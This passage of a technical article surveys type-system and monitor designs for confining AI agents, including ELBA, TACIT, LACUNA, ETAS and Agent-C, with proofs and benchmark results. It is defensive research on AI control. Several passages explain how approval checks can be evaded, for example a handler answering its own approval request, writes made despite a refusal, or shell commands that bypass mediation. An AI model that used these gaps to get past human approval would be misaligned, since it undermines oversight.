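The call to the sub-agent is the last step of a program of type `BibIO ()`, so the compiler infers that the sub-agent's program must have this type too. The parent can impose a tighter limit. If it requests a String, the sub-agent's program cannot search DBLP or write to the file. With RIO, the parent can request a function of type `Path -> RIO ()` and apply it to a Path for a single subdirectory.

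The parent cannot loosen the limit. If it adds the step `agent defs prompt :: IO ()`, its own program fails the type check for the same reason as the program with `writeFile`. The same applies to every generation of sub-agents.

Recursion weakens one advantage of checking programs before they run, because a parent agent may already have acted by the time its sub-agent writes a program. If the sub-agent then fails to produce well-typed code, the run can stop with the work half done. The extra model calls also take time. On AgentDojo, ELBA took about three times as long as CaMeL, an earlier defence against prompt injection in which the model writes one program in advance.

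### The whole-system theorem

In an appendix, Zhou and colleagues prove that adding agent calls to a typed language preserves what its types guarantee. Let L be the language without agent calls. A trace is the sequence of tool calls with observable side effects that a run makes, and traces(e) is the set of traces that a program e can produce. A type t guarantees a property P in L if:

⊢ e : t ⇒ P(traces(e)), for every program e in L

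For `BibIO ()`, P could be "every entry written to the file comes from DBLP". Let L_agent be L with the `agent` function added. The theorem is:

If t guarantees P in L, then t also guarantees P in L_agent.

The proof replaces each agent call with ordinary code in L that queries the model, checks the program it returns and uses that program if it passes. Since the returned program may contain more agent calls, the proof must also replace those. Each call has a limit on the depth of further calls, and this limit shrinks at every level, so the replacement eventually ends. The result is a program in L with the same type and traces as the original. P holds for this program, so it also holds for the original.

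The theorem has several premises:

- The surrounding program and the generated programs are all in the same language, and each generated program passes the type check before it runs.
- Every agent call has a finite depth limit and may return a value that signals failure. Its formal result type is therefore Option t, meaning "a t or nothing".
- The model can be any computable function, but it always gives the same answer to the same input.
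- Traces contain only tool calls.

Real models are not this consistent, but this doesn't affect a property such as "no run uses the network", because every answer has to pass the same check. Inconsistent answers could matter for properties that compare runs, such as "a public output never depends on a secret". Zhou and colleagues suggest storing the model's answers and reusing them where a property requires determinism.

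The traces leave out the model query, so the type of an agent call that returns an Int shows no effects, even though the call sends its prompt to a model. If that model runs on another company's servers, any confidential data in the prompt leaves the machine.

The surrounding code must be in the same language, because otherwise it can undo the limit. Suppose a Python program requests a String from a typed agent and writes it into the bibliography. The agent's program has no effects and passes its check, but the file may now contain an invented entry. If the surrounding code is in Haskell and has the type `BibIO ()`, it cannot use `writeFile` either. Zhou and colleagues consider this the most important difference from earlier systems.

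Some code remains outside the limit. A complete Haskell program has an IO type, so its outermost part must convert the BibIO computation into an IO one. The IO type guarantees very little about that part, so people have to inspect it. People must also inspect tools written in other languages. For the AgentDojo tests, Zhou and colleagues connected their Haskell system to the benchmark's Python code, which Haskell's type checker does not examine.

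### Errors and endless loops

In Haskell, an agent with the result type Int can still raise exceptions, although Zhou and colleagues write that it cannot. According to the *Expressions* chapter of the Haskell 2010 language report, every Haskell type includes computations that fail or never finish. The standard function `error` has the type `String -> a` for any type `a`, so the checker accepts `error "no answer"` as an Int. HaskellWiki's example `let x = x + 1 in x` also has the type Int but never produces a number.

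The safe subset does not change this. The GHC developers' notes page *SafeHaskell* makes an exception for code that halts a program by "throwing uncaught exceptions or looping forever". Ordinary mistakes can also halt a program. In the recursive program above, `head dois` raises an error if the search finds nothing. ELBA's `agent` function raises an error when the model runs out of retries, but its result type `t` does not show that it can fail, unlike the `Option t` in the theorem.

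A user of a calculator on a public website could therefore tie up the server by requesting an endless computation, so the operator needs limits on time and memory in addition to the type. The language report also expects implementations to display the text passed to `error`, so a program of type Int could put arbitrary text into a log. Haskell computes a value only when something needs it, so an error may not appear until the surrounding program uses the agent's result.

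The program still cannot delete files or contact a server in any of these cases. Its type guarantees that it makes no tool calls with side effects and that, if it finishes normally, it returns an integer. Zhou and colleagues mention richer type systems that could also guarantee termination or limit the resources a program uses, but ELBA does not include them.

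## Permissions as values tracked by the type checker

A Path in ELBA is a permission that a program can pass around, but a program's type does not show which Paths it uses. A program of type `RIO ()` might read the source folder, the secrets folder or both. The programming language Scala has an experimental extension, capture checking, that adds this information to types. Researchers at EPFL, the Swiss university where Scala originated, have used it in two systems for AI agents, TACIT and LACUNA.

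### Object capabilities

Permission values come from operating systems. Miller and Shapiro, in *Paradigm Regained*, trace them to a 1966 proposal by Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn for computers that run several users' programs at once. Each running computation would have a list of capabilities, each of which would point to an object, such as a segment of memory, and specify what the computation could do with it. Miller and Shapiro restate this for programming languages as the object-capability model, in which a reference to an object identifies the object and gives permission to use it.

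Two Unix commands that copy a file show how permissions passed as values differ from ordinary access control. The command `cp foo.txt bar.txt` gives `cp` two file names. `cp` has to open the files itself, so it needs permission to open any file the user might name. In `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`, the shell opens both files and passes the open files to `cat`. `cat` needs no other permissions for this job, although current operating systems give it all of the user's permissions.

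References can work as permissions only if the language prevents programs from inventing them, as C++ programs can by turning a number into a memory address. The language must also prevent programs from directly accessing another object's private data or communicating through global variables that any code can change. With these restrictions, every access derives from an earlier one, so a program that holds no reference to the network, and none to anything that would pass one on, can never obtain one.

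A program can also act through the objects it holds. Suppose a program receives only a logger, an object that records messages. If the logger holds a reference to a file, the program can change that file by logging a message. Miller and Shapiro therefore distinguish a program's permissions, which cover what it can access directly, from its authority, which includes what it can cause through other objects. Older capability languages such as E check capabilities only while a program runs, so people have to trace the code to find out what a logger can reach.

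### Types with capture sets

Capture checking puts this information into the logger's type. Scala's *Tracked Capabilities Overview* gives this example:

```
val out: File^ = new File("~/some/bits")
val lg: Logger^{out} = new Logger(out)
```

Each line defines a name, with its type after the colon. The type `Logger^{out}` describes a logger that may use the capability `out`. In general, T^{c₁, …, cₙ} is the type of values of type T that may hold on to the capabilities in the capture set {c₁, …, cₙ}. An ordinary type without a set, such as `Logger`, is pure, meaning its values hold no capabilities. The type `Logger^` is short for `Logger^{any}` and allows any capabilities. *Capturing Types* (Boruch-Gruszecki, Odersky and colleagues, 2023) developed a formal language for such types, which guided the design of Scala's checker.

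Like an effect row, a capture set is an upper bound. A value that may use fewer capabilities can therefore stand in for a value that may use more. This puts the types in an order, where S <: T means that a program can use an S wherever it needs a T. If f is some other capability, then for any ordinary type A:

A <: A^{lg} <: A^{out} <: A^{out, f} <: A^

Most of these steps only add capabilities to the set, but the step from {lg} to {out} replaces one with another. It is valid because `lg` has the type `Logger^{out}`, so a program could do anything with `out` that it does with `lg`. The reverse does not hold, because the logger can only record messages, while the file may allow other operations.

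Scala's *Capture Checking Basics* states the general rules. Leaving out a special case for classes, they are:

- C₁ <: C₂ if every capability c in C₁ is either in C₂ or has a type whose own capture set D satisfies D <: C₂.
- T₁^C₁ <: T₂^C₂ if T₁ <: T₂ and C₁ <: C₂.

These rules do the same job as the widening rule for effect sets, but a capability stands for a particular resource rather than a kind of operation such as Read. The maintenance agent's harness could create two capabilities, `src` for the source folder and `secrets` for the folder of passwords. A function that reads source files would then have the type `Path ->{src} Text`, and one that reads passwords `Path ->{secrets} Text`. With the five effects used so far, both have the type `Path → Text ! {Read}`. But the set `{src}` does not show whether a function only reads the folder or also writes to it. To show that, the designer needs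 separate capabilities for reading and writing.

### Pure functions and global capabilities

A function's capture set contains the capabilities that its body uses, apart from those it receives as arguments. Scala writes the set after the arrow:

| Type | What the function may hold |
|---|---|
| `A -> B` | no capabilities |
| `A ->{c, d} B` | only `c` and `d` |
| `A => B` | any capabilities |

Existing Scala code uses `=>` for all functions. Under capture checking, this arrow means that the function may capture any capability, so `map` can accept both pure and effectful functions without a change to its type. According to SoftwareMill's *Understanding Capture Checking in Scala*, the designers chose this meaning to keep changes to existing code small, and Scala 3.8 includes a fully capture-checked standard library.

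A pure function in this sense can still act on its argument, so a function of type `File^ -> Unit` may write to whatever file its caller passes in. If the argument is plain text, the function has nothing to act on. It also cannot store information in a variable outside itself, because Scala treats such variables as capabilities too. A function of type `Text -> Patch` can therefore only compute a patch from a text.

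Types can guarantee that one part of a program has no side effects even if the rest does, which Odersky and colleagues call local purity. For example, the maintenance agent's harness could require `fix`, the function that edits the text, to have the type `Text -> Patch`. The surrounding program could still read files, ask a person and write patches, but `fix` could do none of these. TACIT uses the same kind of type to let programs process confidential files without revealing their contents.

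Tracking also makes global capabilities acceptable. Traditional object-capability languages exclude them because any code could use a global console, even without being passed a reference to it. Programs in these languages must instead pass each capability from the program's entry point through every function leading to the code that needs it. Converting an existing program to this style usually means rewriting much of it.

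In Scala, a program can define a global `Console`, because functions that use it have types that include it. For example, the function `() => Console.out.println("hi")`, which prints a greeting, has the type `() ->{Console.out} Unit`, so the compiler rejects it wherever the program requires a pure function. A global object that uses the console must declare this in a `uses` clause, so a helper object can't hide the dependency. But code can still print freely where the types set no limit.

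### A permission that lasts for one block

TACIT's function for file access, slightly simplified, has this type:

```
def requestFileSystem[T](root: String)(block: FileSystem^ => T): T
```

The function creates a capability for the directory `root`, passes it to a block of code and returns the block's result. The capability becomes invalid when the block ends. T can be any type that makes sense outside the block. A program that returns a file's text is fine, with T equal to String:

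```
val text = requestFileSystem("/data"): fs =>
  fs.access("notes.txt").read()
```

Odersky and colleagues also give an example of a program that tries to keep the permission:

```
val bad = requestFileSystem("/data"): fs =>
  () => fs.access("secret.txt").read()
bad()
```

This block reads nothing. It returns a closure, a function that holds on to values from the place where the program defined it. The closure would read the file later, when the last line calls it. The checker rejects the program by the following reasoning:

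1. The parameter `fs` has the type `FileSystem^`, so it is a capability.
2. The closure uses `fs`, so its type is `() ->{fs} String`.
3. The block returns the closure, so T would have to be `() ->{fs} String`.
4. The name `fs` exists only inside the block, but T must make sense outside it. No suitable T exists.

The checker can sometimes replace a local name with one that is visible outside the local scope. If a function receives the capability `fs` and creates a local logger from it, the checker widens the result's type from `Logger^{localLogger}` to `Logger^{fs}`. In the rejected program, `fs` has the type `FileSystem^`, which identifies no capability outside the block, so the checker has no outside name to substitute.

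Storing the capability in a variable outside the block does not work either. Scala's *Scoped Capabilities* explains that every capability has a level, set by where the program defines it. A capability can flow into more deeply nested code but not outwards, so the compiler rejects the assignment. It also rejects a data structure that contains the capability. In one of TACIT's benchmark runs, an agent tried to return a list of file handles from the block. Each handle's type included the file system capability, so the program failed the check.

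The checker also accounts for when code runs. Suppose a block goes through a list of numbers, writes each one to a file and returns their squares. With an ordinary list, all the writing happens inside the block and the result contains only numbers, so the checker accepts the program. A lazy list computes each item when the program first needs it, so it would have to keep access to the file after the block ends, and the checker rejects the program.

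Some rejections prevent no harm. Another agent wrote a helper function that prints the first five lines of a file, but declared its parameter as `FileEntry` instead of `FileEntry^`. The compiler rejected the program because a pure type cannot accept a handle that holds a capability. The program would have printed lines only from files it was allowed to read, and adding the missing `^` would presumably have fixed it.

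TACIT relies on run-time checks, not types, to limit which files a program can reach. Its library stops any request for a path outside `root`, much as ELBA's `//` operation does. The program also supplies `root` itself, as an ordinary string, so the type checker would accept a request for the entire disk. Only the library's code can limit which directory the program chooses. For the maintenance agent, whose harness must never allow network access, the simplest solution is a library with no function for requesting it.

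### TACIT

The name TACIT stands for Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types. The system is a server for the Model Context Protocol, a standard for connecting agents to tools, so existing agents such as Claude Code can use it without modification. It works as follows:

1. The agent sends a snippet of Scala code as the argument of a tool call.
2. The compiler checks the snippet with capture checking and in safe mode, which disables language features that could bypass the types.
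3. If the snippet passes, an interactive interpreter runs it. The interpreter can keep the snippet's definitions for later snippets in the same session.
4. The server sends the output, or the compiler's error messages, back to the agent.

The running snippet can reach the outside world only through a small library. Besides `requestFileSystem`, the library has functions that request access to listed commands and to listed network hosts. Each function passes a capability to a block of code, and the capability expires when the block returns. The next snippet can therefore use text that an earlier one read, but it cannot reuse the earlier snippet's permission to read files.

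Calling any of these functions requires another capability, `IOCapability`, which is available at the top level of a snippet but not inside a pure function. Without this restriction, a function of type `Text -> Patch` could request network access inside its body.

Unlike ELBA, TACIT does not check the program that surrounds the agent's code. This makes TACIT easy to add to an existing agent, but an unmodified agent keeps its other tools. If Claude Code can still run shell commands directly, TACIT's types place no limit on those commands. The operator has to turn such tools off to achieve complete mediation. In a test on programming tasks, Odersky and colleagues told the agent that it had no built-in tools and had to use TACIT for every operation.

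They set out three requirements for a language that runs agents' code:

- **Capability safety:** Programs cannot forge capabilities or evade the requirement to have one.
- **Capability completeness:** Capabilities regulate every effect that matters for safety, except those that the system can contain at run time.
- **Local purity:** Types can limit a particular computation to a given set of capabilities, which may be empty.

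The guarantee for pure functions depends on all three. If a program could forge a `FileSystem`, it could create one inside a pure function. If some library function opened network connections without a capability, another function could call it and still be typed as pure. Without local purity, a harness could only limit the program as a whole.

Errors are the main effects that TACIT contains at run time instead of tracking in types. Division by zero or a lack of memory can interrupt almost any computation, and Odersky and colleagues consider it impractical to track such errors in types. TACIT instead turns an error into an ordinary value that represents failure, which the rest of the program can handle.

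Odersky and colleagues describe Scala 3 as the only production-ready language with statically tracked capabilities. In their view, Haskell can provide local purity but has no built-in object capabilities, so a designer would have to encode them with more advanced types. ELBA's Path shows that private constructors are enough for a basic version of these capabilities. But a Haskell program can keep a Path indefinitely unless the library's types also restrict this.

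### LACUNA

Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *LACUNA*, describe a system that brings the agent's loop into the checked program. Its central function closely resembles the one in ELBA:

```
def agent[T](task: String): T
```

A call to `agent` is a typed hole, a gap in a program for which only the type is known. When the program reaches the hole, LACUNA sends the model the task, the expected type, the surrounding source code and a list of the names available at that point. The model replies with Scala code. LACUNA inserts this code into the hole and compiles the result with the same compiler and settings as the original program. As in ELBA, the code runs only if it compiles, and otherwise the model receives the error messages and tries again.

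In ELBA, the developer lists the definitions that the model may use. In LACUNA, the model's code may use every name in scope at the hole, so these names are its permission set. The maintenance agent could have a function like this, where a `Reader` is a capability for reading the source folder:

```
def propose(src: Reader^): Patch =
  agent("Find the parsing bug and propose a patch.")
```

The model's code can use `src` and anything that the file defines or imports at its top level. With capture checking and safe mode turned on, the code cannot write files or use the network unless one of these provides a way to do so. The result's type, `Patch`, has no capture set, so the result cannot keep a reference to `src`. A later phase of the work could use a hole in another function, whose parameters give it different permissions.

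This arrangement is convenient, but developers can easily grant permissions by accident. If a developer opens a network connection and then calls `agent` in the same scope, the model's code can use the connection even if the task does not need it. Zhao and colleagues acknowledge that the type system only restricts the code to what is in scope and does not work out which permissions a task needs. Putting the call in a separate function, as in `propose`, hides the caller's local variables. Functions that create capabilities also count as permissions, so the developer has to keep them out of scope or make them require a capability.

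Rejected code has no effects, as in ELBA. In one example, a variable `balance` is 100, and the program asks for code that subtracts 50 and returns the new balance as a whole number. The model writes:

```
balance -= 50
s"remaining: $balance"
```

The last line produces text instead of a number, so the compiler rejects the code. The balance is still 100, and the next attempt starts from that balance.

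This protection does not cover code that passes the check. An accepted snippet can still send one message and then stop because a server does not respond.

Zhao and colleagues wrote about 400 pairs of surrounding code and inserted code to test the check without a model. Some pairs were valid, and others contained errors that agents commonly make. The compiler gave the expected result for every pair.

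### Effects on task performance

Types could make an agent less useful if models struggle to write programs that pass the check. Odersky and colleagues tested this on τ²-bench, which simulates conversations between a customer-service agent and a customer. The same models worked either with ordinary tool calls or by writing Scala for TACIT. The table shows the percentage of tasks they solved, averaged over ten runs of each task:

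| Model | Airline, tool calls | Airline, TACIT | Retail, tool calls | Retail, TACIT |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8 | 45.2 | 53.3 | 57.0 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4 | 61.0 | 75.1 | 77.5 |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8 | 58.6 | 74.6 | 75.5 |

TACIT did better in all six comparisons, by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points. Odersky and colleagues attribute this to the typed interface, which returns structured records instead of raw data, and to the compiler's error messages. The comparison does not isolate the effect of capture checking, because the published functions for these tasks, such as `cancelReservation(reservationId: String): Reservation`, have no capabilities in their parameters or results. The test therefore mainly shows that models can act by writing typed Scala.

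Programming tasks make more use of file and command capabilities. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software issues, MiniMax M2.5 solved 43.3% with ordinary tools and 41.7% with TACIT. The five-issue difference could easily be chance. Odersky and colleagues suggest that programming tasks rely on shell commands, which are less natural to express through TACIT's library.

Few snippets failed to compile on τ²-bench. The share that needed a retry ranged from 0.32%, for gpt-oss-120b on retail tasks, to 7.93%, for DeepSeek V3.2 on airline tasks. Those snippets needed between 1.06 and 1.39 retries on average. Recurring mistakes included failing to handle a possibly missing value and writing one dollar sign in a string where Scala requires two. Checking a typical snippet took less than a second, so most of the delay from a retry came from calling the model again.

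LACUNA's results on the same benchmark were worse. Zhao and colleagues ran each of 392 tasks once, including tasks from two telecom domains. These are the percentages solved:

| Domain | DeepSeek-V4-Flash, tool calls | DeepSeek-V4-Flash, LACUNA | Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, tool calls | Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, LACUNA |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Retail | 80.9 | 58.8 | 52.6 | 43.9 |
| Airline | 75.5 | 70.0 | 56.0 | 38.0 |
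| Telecom | 100.0 | 88.6 | 15.8 | 14.9 |
| Telecom workflow | 95.4 | 83.3 | 21.1 | 24.6 |
| All tasks | 90.0 | 76.0 | 33.2 | 29.1 |

With DeepSeek, LACUNA solved 76.0% of tasks and the ordinary agent solved 90.0%, a difference of about 55 tasks, though Zhao and colleagues describe the two as on par. The compiler rejected 22.4% of DeepSeek's retail snippets. For Gemini, the rejection rate ranged from 3.2% on retail tasks to 89% on telecom tasks, where most conversation turns made no progress.

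Rejections do not explain the whole loss, however. Gemini's success rate on retail tasks was 8.7 percentage points lower with LACUNA, even though nearly all of its retail code compiled. LACUNA also keeps the conversation in the variables and output of a running program, while TACIT leaves the agent's usual loop in place. Zhao and colleagues accept that an ordinary loop may manage a long conversation more efficiently. The lower scores may therefore come largely from this change rather than from the types, but the experiment cannot separate the two.

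Zhao and colleagues also tested LACUNA on BrowseComp-Plus, a set of 830 difficult questions that an agent answers by searching a fixed collection of about 100,000 documents. DeepSeek-V4-Flash answered 27.1% correctly, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite 26.2% and GPT-5.4 mini 9.2%. The compiler rejected 8.6% of DeepSeek's snippets, and DeepSeek needed no retry on two-thirds of the questions. They conclude that type checking did not reduce accuracy. But they did not run the same models with ordinary tool calls on this benchmark, so the result shows only that LACUNA can carry out long searches.

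None of these experiments used a leading model from late 2026. The TACIT comparison included gpt-oss-120b and DeepSeek V3.2, which date from 2025, and MiniMax M2.5, from early 2026. The LACUNA tests used models available in spring 2026, but Zhao and colleagues chose small, cheap versions and turned off their reasoning for τ²-bench. Stronger models would probably write fewer programs that fail to compile, but neither paper measures how much of LACUNA's loss would remain.

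Adopting TACIT also takes some programming. The shared part, which includes the capability library, is about 1,000 lines of Scala, and writing it requires understanding capture checking. Each new domain needs an interface that describes its tools. The airline and retail interfaces are a few hundred lines each, about as long as the tool descriptions they replace. Odersky and colleagues suggest that agents can help write these interfaces but expect people to review them before an agent runs, because the interfaces determine what the agent can do.

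## Checking the order of actions and approvals

A capture set lists what a program may use, but it does not record when the program uses it. Neither does an effect row. The maintenance agent must ask a person before it writes a patch. The first of these programs obeys that rule and the second breaks it:

```
let ok = ask(patch) in if ok then write(patch) else ()

let done = write(patch) in let ok = ask(patch) in ()
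```

The sequencing rule takes the union of the two parts' effects. The first program gets {Ask} ∪ {Write} and the second gets {Write} ∪ {Ask}, which is the same set. A program that writes without asking also passes, because {Write} is a subset of {Ask, Write}.

A set of effects doesn't record their order, so an effect system that tracks order needs a richer structure. *Effect Systems as Abstract Interpretations* (Gordon, 2026) explains that such a system uses one operator for branching and another for sequencing. Early examples described the order of messages in Concurrent ML, a language for programs with several parts running at once. *Types and trace effects of higher order programs* (Skalka, Smith and Van Horn, 2008) used effects that describe whole sequences of events. ETAS, a language by Tan and colleagues, applies this idea to agents and extends it to operations that a handler intercepts.

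### Request summaries

The effect judgment in ETAS has one more part than the usual one:

Γ ⊢ e : τ ! ε ▷ A

As before, Γ lists the variables in scope and τ is the type of the result. The row ε contains the effects that can escape, meaning those that no handler inside e intercepts. The new part, A, is a request summary, which describes the orders in which e may request operations. It uses the following notation, with a for an approval request and w for a request to write a patch:

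| Expression | Meaning |
|---|---|
| 1 | no requests |
| a | one approval request |
| w | one write request |
| A ; B | the requests in A, followed by those in B |
| A ⊔ B | the requests in A or those in B |
| A* | A repeated any number of times, including zero |

The checker computes the row and the summary together. Where the sequencing rule takes the union of two rows, it joins the two summaries with a semicolon. Where the branching rule takes a union, it joins the summaries with ⊔. For the first program above, this gives:

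| Part | Row | Summary |
|---|---|---|
| `write(patch)` | {Write} | w |
| `()` | ∅ | 1 |
| `if ok then … else …` | {Write} | 1 ⊔ w |
| whole program | {Ask, Write} | a ; (1 ⊔ w) |

The summary describes two possible sequences, a and aw. The second program has the summary w ; a, so the checker can now distinguish the two programs.

Like a row, a summary is an upper bound, so it may include sequences that never occur. It is often less precise for loops and recursive functions, where ETAS accepts a summary that covers every repetition. In the worst case, this summary is "any operations in any order".

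### Requests that a handler intercepts

In a preview, the DryRun handler mentioned earlier intercepts the write, so the row shrinks from {Ask, Write} to {Ask}. The smaller row correctly describes the effects on the repository, which stays unchanged. But if the checker used only the remaining effects to check order, a program that writes before asking would pass in a dry run, and the mistake would appear only once somebody removed the handler.

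Tan and colleagues therefore keep intercepted requests in the summary. If the program has the summary A and the handler's own code has the summary Aₕ, the combination has the summary:

pref(A ∥ Aₕ*)

The symbol ∥ means that the two sets of requests can interleave in any way that preserves the order within each. The star allows for the handler running any number of times. The function pref adds every prefix of every sequence, because a handler can end the computation early.

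DryRun makes no requests of its own, so Aₕ is 1 and the formula reduces to pref(a ; (1 ⊔ w)). This describes the empty sequence, a, and aw. The write no longer appears in the row but remains in the summary, so the order rule applies to the preview as it does to the real run.

The order check is stricter than preventing harm requires. If a contract forbids all writes, ETAS rejects even a write that a handler would have discarded. This strictness also means that DryRun can't make a program pass the check just by hiding its writes.

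### The contract and its automaton

A developer states the permitted orders in a trace contract. The clause `+op` allows an operation, `-op` forbids it, and `g >> w` allows both g and w but requires every w to have an earlier g. The developer can combine clauses with `&` or list alternatives with `|`. Any operation that no clause allows is forbidden. The contract for applying patches needs only one clause:

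```
Approval.request >> Repo.apply
```

These are the ETAS names for the operations a and w. The compiler translates the clause into the same notation as the summaries. With E for the set of all operations and ∩ for the sequences that two expressions have in common, the translation is:

P = (a ⊔ w)* ∩ (E∖{w})* ; (1 ⊔ a ; E*) = 1 ⊔ a ; (a ⊔ w)*

The expression (a ⊔ w)* allows only approval requests and writes. The expression after ∩ rules out any write before the first approval request. Together they permit either no actions or an approval request followed by any mixture of approval requests and writes. The full six-line program also reads a file, so its contract would need a clause allowing reads.

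A program satisfies the contract if P permits every sequence in the program's summary and every beginning of such a sequence. To check this, the compiler turns P into a finite automaton, which has a few states and moves between them as requests occur. Schneider's *Enforceable Security Policies* uses the term "security automaton" for an automaton that specifies a security policy in this way. Its example policy forbids sending messages after reading a file. The automaton starts in a "no file read" state, moves to a "file read" state at the first read, and has no transition for sending from there.

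In ETAS, each state stands for the set of continuations that the contract still permits. The contract for patches needs three:

| State | Meaning | After a | After w |
|---|---|---|---|
| q₀ | no approval request yet | qₐ | Bad |
| qₐ | at least one approval request | qₐ | qₐ |
| Bad | contract broken | Bad | Bad |

Any other operation also leads to Bad. The compiler starts in q₀, follows every sequence in the program's summary and collects the states in which they end. No sequence can leave Bad, so one that ends in another state has obeyed the contract throughout. There are three possible outcomes:

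| Summary | Sequences | Final states | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|
| a ; (1 ⊔ w) | a, aw | {qₐ} | proved |
| w ; a | wa | {Bad} | rejected |
| (a ; w) ⊔ (w ; a) | aw, wa | {qₐ, Bad} | left to a runtime monitor |

In the third case, the compiler accepts the program but requires a residual monitor, which runs the same automaton alongside the program and stops it at the first request that leads to Bad. Bodden, Lam and Hendren had already used static analysis in *Clara* to limit a monitor to the places in a program that the analysis could not prove safe. ETAS keeps the whole automaton, because the monitor has to track approval requests to determine whether a write is allowed.

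The third outcome can include programs that never request approval. For example, the model might write `if urgent then write(patch) else ()`. The summary is 1 ⊔ w, and the final states are {q₀, Bad}. The formal rules do not reject this program, because one of its paths is harmless. The monitor blocks the write if the program attempts it, but by then the program may have carried out other permitted actions. An operator who wants the whole decision made before the run would have to treat the third outcome as a rejection.

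A contract belongs to a function, and its monitor starts in q₀ each time the program calls that function. If the program asks for approval and then calls a function that has this contract but only writes, the earlier request does not count. The function has to contain both steps, or the developer has to attach the contract to the code that calls it.

### What one approval request permits

Once the automaton is in qₐ, every later write leaves it there. A program that asks for approval once and then writes fifty patches satisfies the contract. So does a program that asks for approval of one patch and writes another, because a and w do not include the operations' arguments.

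The contract also does not depend on the person's answer. Consider this program:

```
let ok = ask(patch) in write(patch)
```

Its summary is a ; w, so the compiler proves that it obeys the contract, although it writes the patch even if the person refuses. The conditional `if ok` prevents this in the correct program, but the contract does not require it, and the model may have written it.

A program could even answer its own request. The order rule counts intercepted requests, so a handler that intercepts `ask` and always returns true satisfies the rule without anyone seeing the patch.

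ETAS deals with these cases through a further check by the host, the trusted software that carries out real operations. A write request goes through the following steps:

1. Every active monitor checks the request against its automaton. If one would move to Bad, the run stops.
2. If a handler in the program intercepts the operation, the handler's code runs and the host does nothing.
3. Otherwise, the host checks that the operation is in the declared row and that a function called grant permits this particular request.
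4. If both checks pass, the host attempts the write. If it succeeds, the host records a commit, meaning an operation that it has actually carried out.

The grant function receives the operation's arguments and the record of the run so far, so it can check whether the program may change this file and whether the person agreed to this patch. The interpreter stores grants separately from approval requests, so neither requesting approval nor answering the request in a handler gives the program permission to write.

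When an untrusted model writes the program, the grant function enforces the person's decision. This function is ordinary host code that runs at the moment of the write, and the order contract does not reveal mistakes in it. The contract can still expose a missing approval step before the program starts and in a dry run.

### Stricter contracts

A contract could demand a new approval request for each write:

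(a ; (1 ⊔ w))*

This contract requires an approval request directly before every write. In the automaton, a write in state qₐ leads back to q₀, so a second write in a row leads to Bad. The checking method also works here, because it accepts any contract that a finite automaton can express and that permits every prefix of a permitted sequence.

However, a developer cannot write this rule with the clauses that ETAS provides. Any combination of clauses that accepts aw also accepts aww, because the approval request comes before both writes. The clauses cannot express Schneider's rule either. If they accept a message followed by a file read, they also accept another message after the read. Adding clauses for such rules would presumably be a small change, since the automaton can already represent them.

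Tying an approval to a particular patch requires a different kind of rule, one that refers to values:

for every patch p: write(p) requires an earlier approval of p

*Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues, 2026) uses rules of this form, written in a temporal logic, a logic for statements about the order of events. An existing monitoring program can check these rules against the record of a run. A finite automaton over operation names is not enough, because the number of possible patches has no limit.

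*Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (Kamath, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) describes Agent-C, a run-time system whose rules about the order of calls can also depend on an earlier call's result. In one example, a customer-service agent may look up an order only after it has successfully looked up the customer by email and the result matches the order's owner. Agent-C checks each proposed tool call before it runs and makes the model generate another if the call would break a rule. A similar rule for the maintenance agent could require that an earlier request about the same patch returned true.

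On customer-service tasks, Agent-C raised the rate at which Claude Sonnet 4.5 followed the rules from 77.4% to 100%, and GPT-5's rate from 83.7% to 100%. The share of tasks completed while following the rules also rose, from 71.8% to 75.2% for Claude Sonnet 4.5 and from 66.1% to 70.6% for GPT-5. The perfect scores follow from the design, because Agent-C blocks any call that breaks a stated rule, but the stated rules may still omit something the company wanted.

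Types can also connect an approval to a patch before the run. With the `Approved Patch` type suggested earlier for ELBA, `write` accepts only an approved patch as its argument. This ensures, without any trace, that a program can write a patch only after that same patch has been approved. But it does not prevent a program from writing the same approved patch twice. An argument type like this also cannot forbid an action because of an unrelated earlier one, as Schneider's rule does.

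All of these rules need reliable approval events. Kekatos and colleagues replayed recorded agent runs from AgentDojo against five general rules, each requiring approval, consent or confirmation before a class of risky action. The records contained no approvals, so the rules flagged every action in those classes. They flagged 70.1% of successful attacks but also 29.3% of harmless runs. On banking tasks, where legitimate users also move money, they flagged 79.2% of harmless runs.

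A monitor can easily misidentify something else as an approval. The software in the same study recognised approvals by looking for certain words in tool names, and at first the pattern "ack" matched unrelated tools for the messaging service Slack. A typed language avoids this error because the contract refers to a declared operation, but the developer still has to make sure that the operation requests approval from someone.

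### The theorems

Tan and colleagues prove several theorems about a core version of ETAS. Let t be the trace of a run, reqs(t) the sequence of requests that the monitors admitted, and commits(t) the set of operations that the host carried out. L(A) is the set of sequences that A describes, and Pref(L(A)) also includes their beginnings. For a complete program with row ε and summary A, every finite run satisfies:

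reqs(t) ∈ Pref(L(A)) and commits(t) ⊆ ε

The statement about commits is the usual soundness guarantee for effect rows. The statement about requests extends that guarantee to the order of operations and to operations that a handler intercepts. The beginnings are necessary because a run may stop early or still be in progress.

A further theorem covers the contract. If P is the contract and its monitor is active, every finite run satisfies:

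reqs(t) ∈ L(P)

This holds whether the compiler proved the contract in advance or left the monitor to check it. If the compiler proved it, removing the monitor doesn't change any successful run or let any forbidden request through, provided later optimisations preserve the summary. The host must still check the row and the grant.

Tan and colleagues also prove that a handler cannot erase a request from the trace or bypass the host's checks. Their type-safety theorems, which are standard, guarantee that a well-typed program always finishes, takes another step or stops with a recorded error.

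The paper's proofs are written in prose and assume complete mediation and host operations that report all their effects and requests. If a program starts a shell command that edits the repository, the edit never appears as w, so the automaton stays in q₀. The theorem about reqs(t) still holds, even though files have changed without approval.

Schneider proved that a monitor that watches a run and stops it can enforce only safety properties, which are rules whose every violation occurs by some definite point in the run. "No write before an approval request" is one example. Such a monitor cannot enforce "Every approved patch eventually reaches the repository," because a run that has not yet written the patch could still do so later. ETAS contracts have the same limit, even when the compiler checks them in advance, because a contract that permits a sequence must also permit every beginning of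 it.

### How much the tests show

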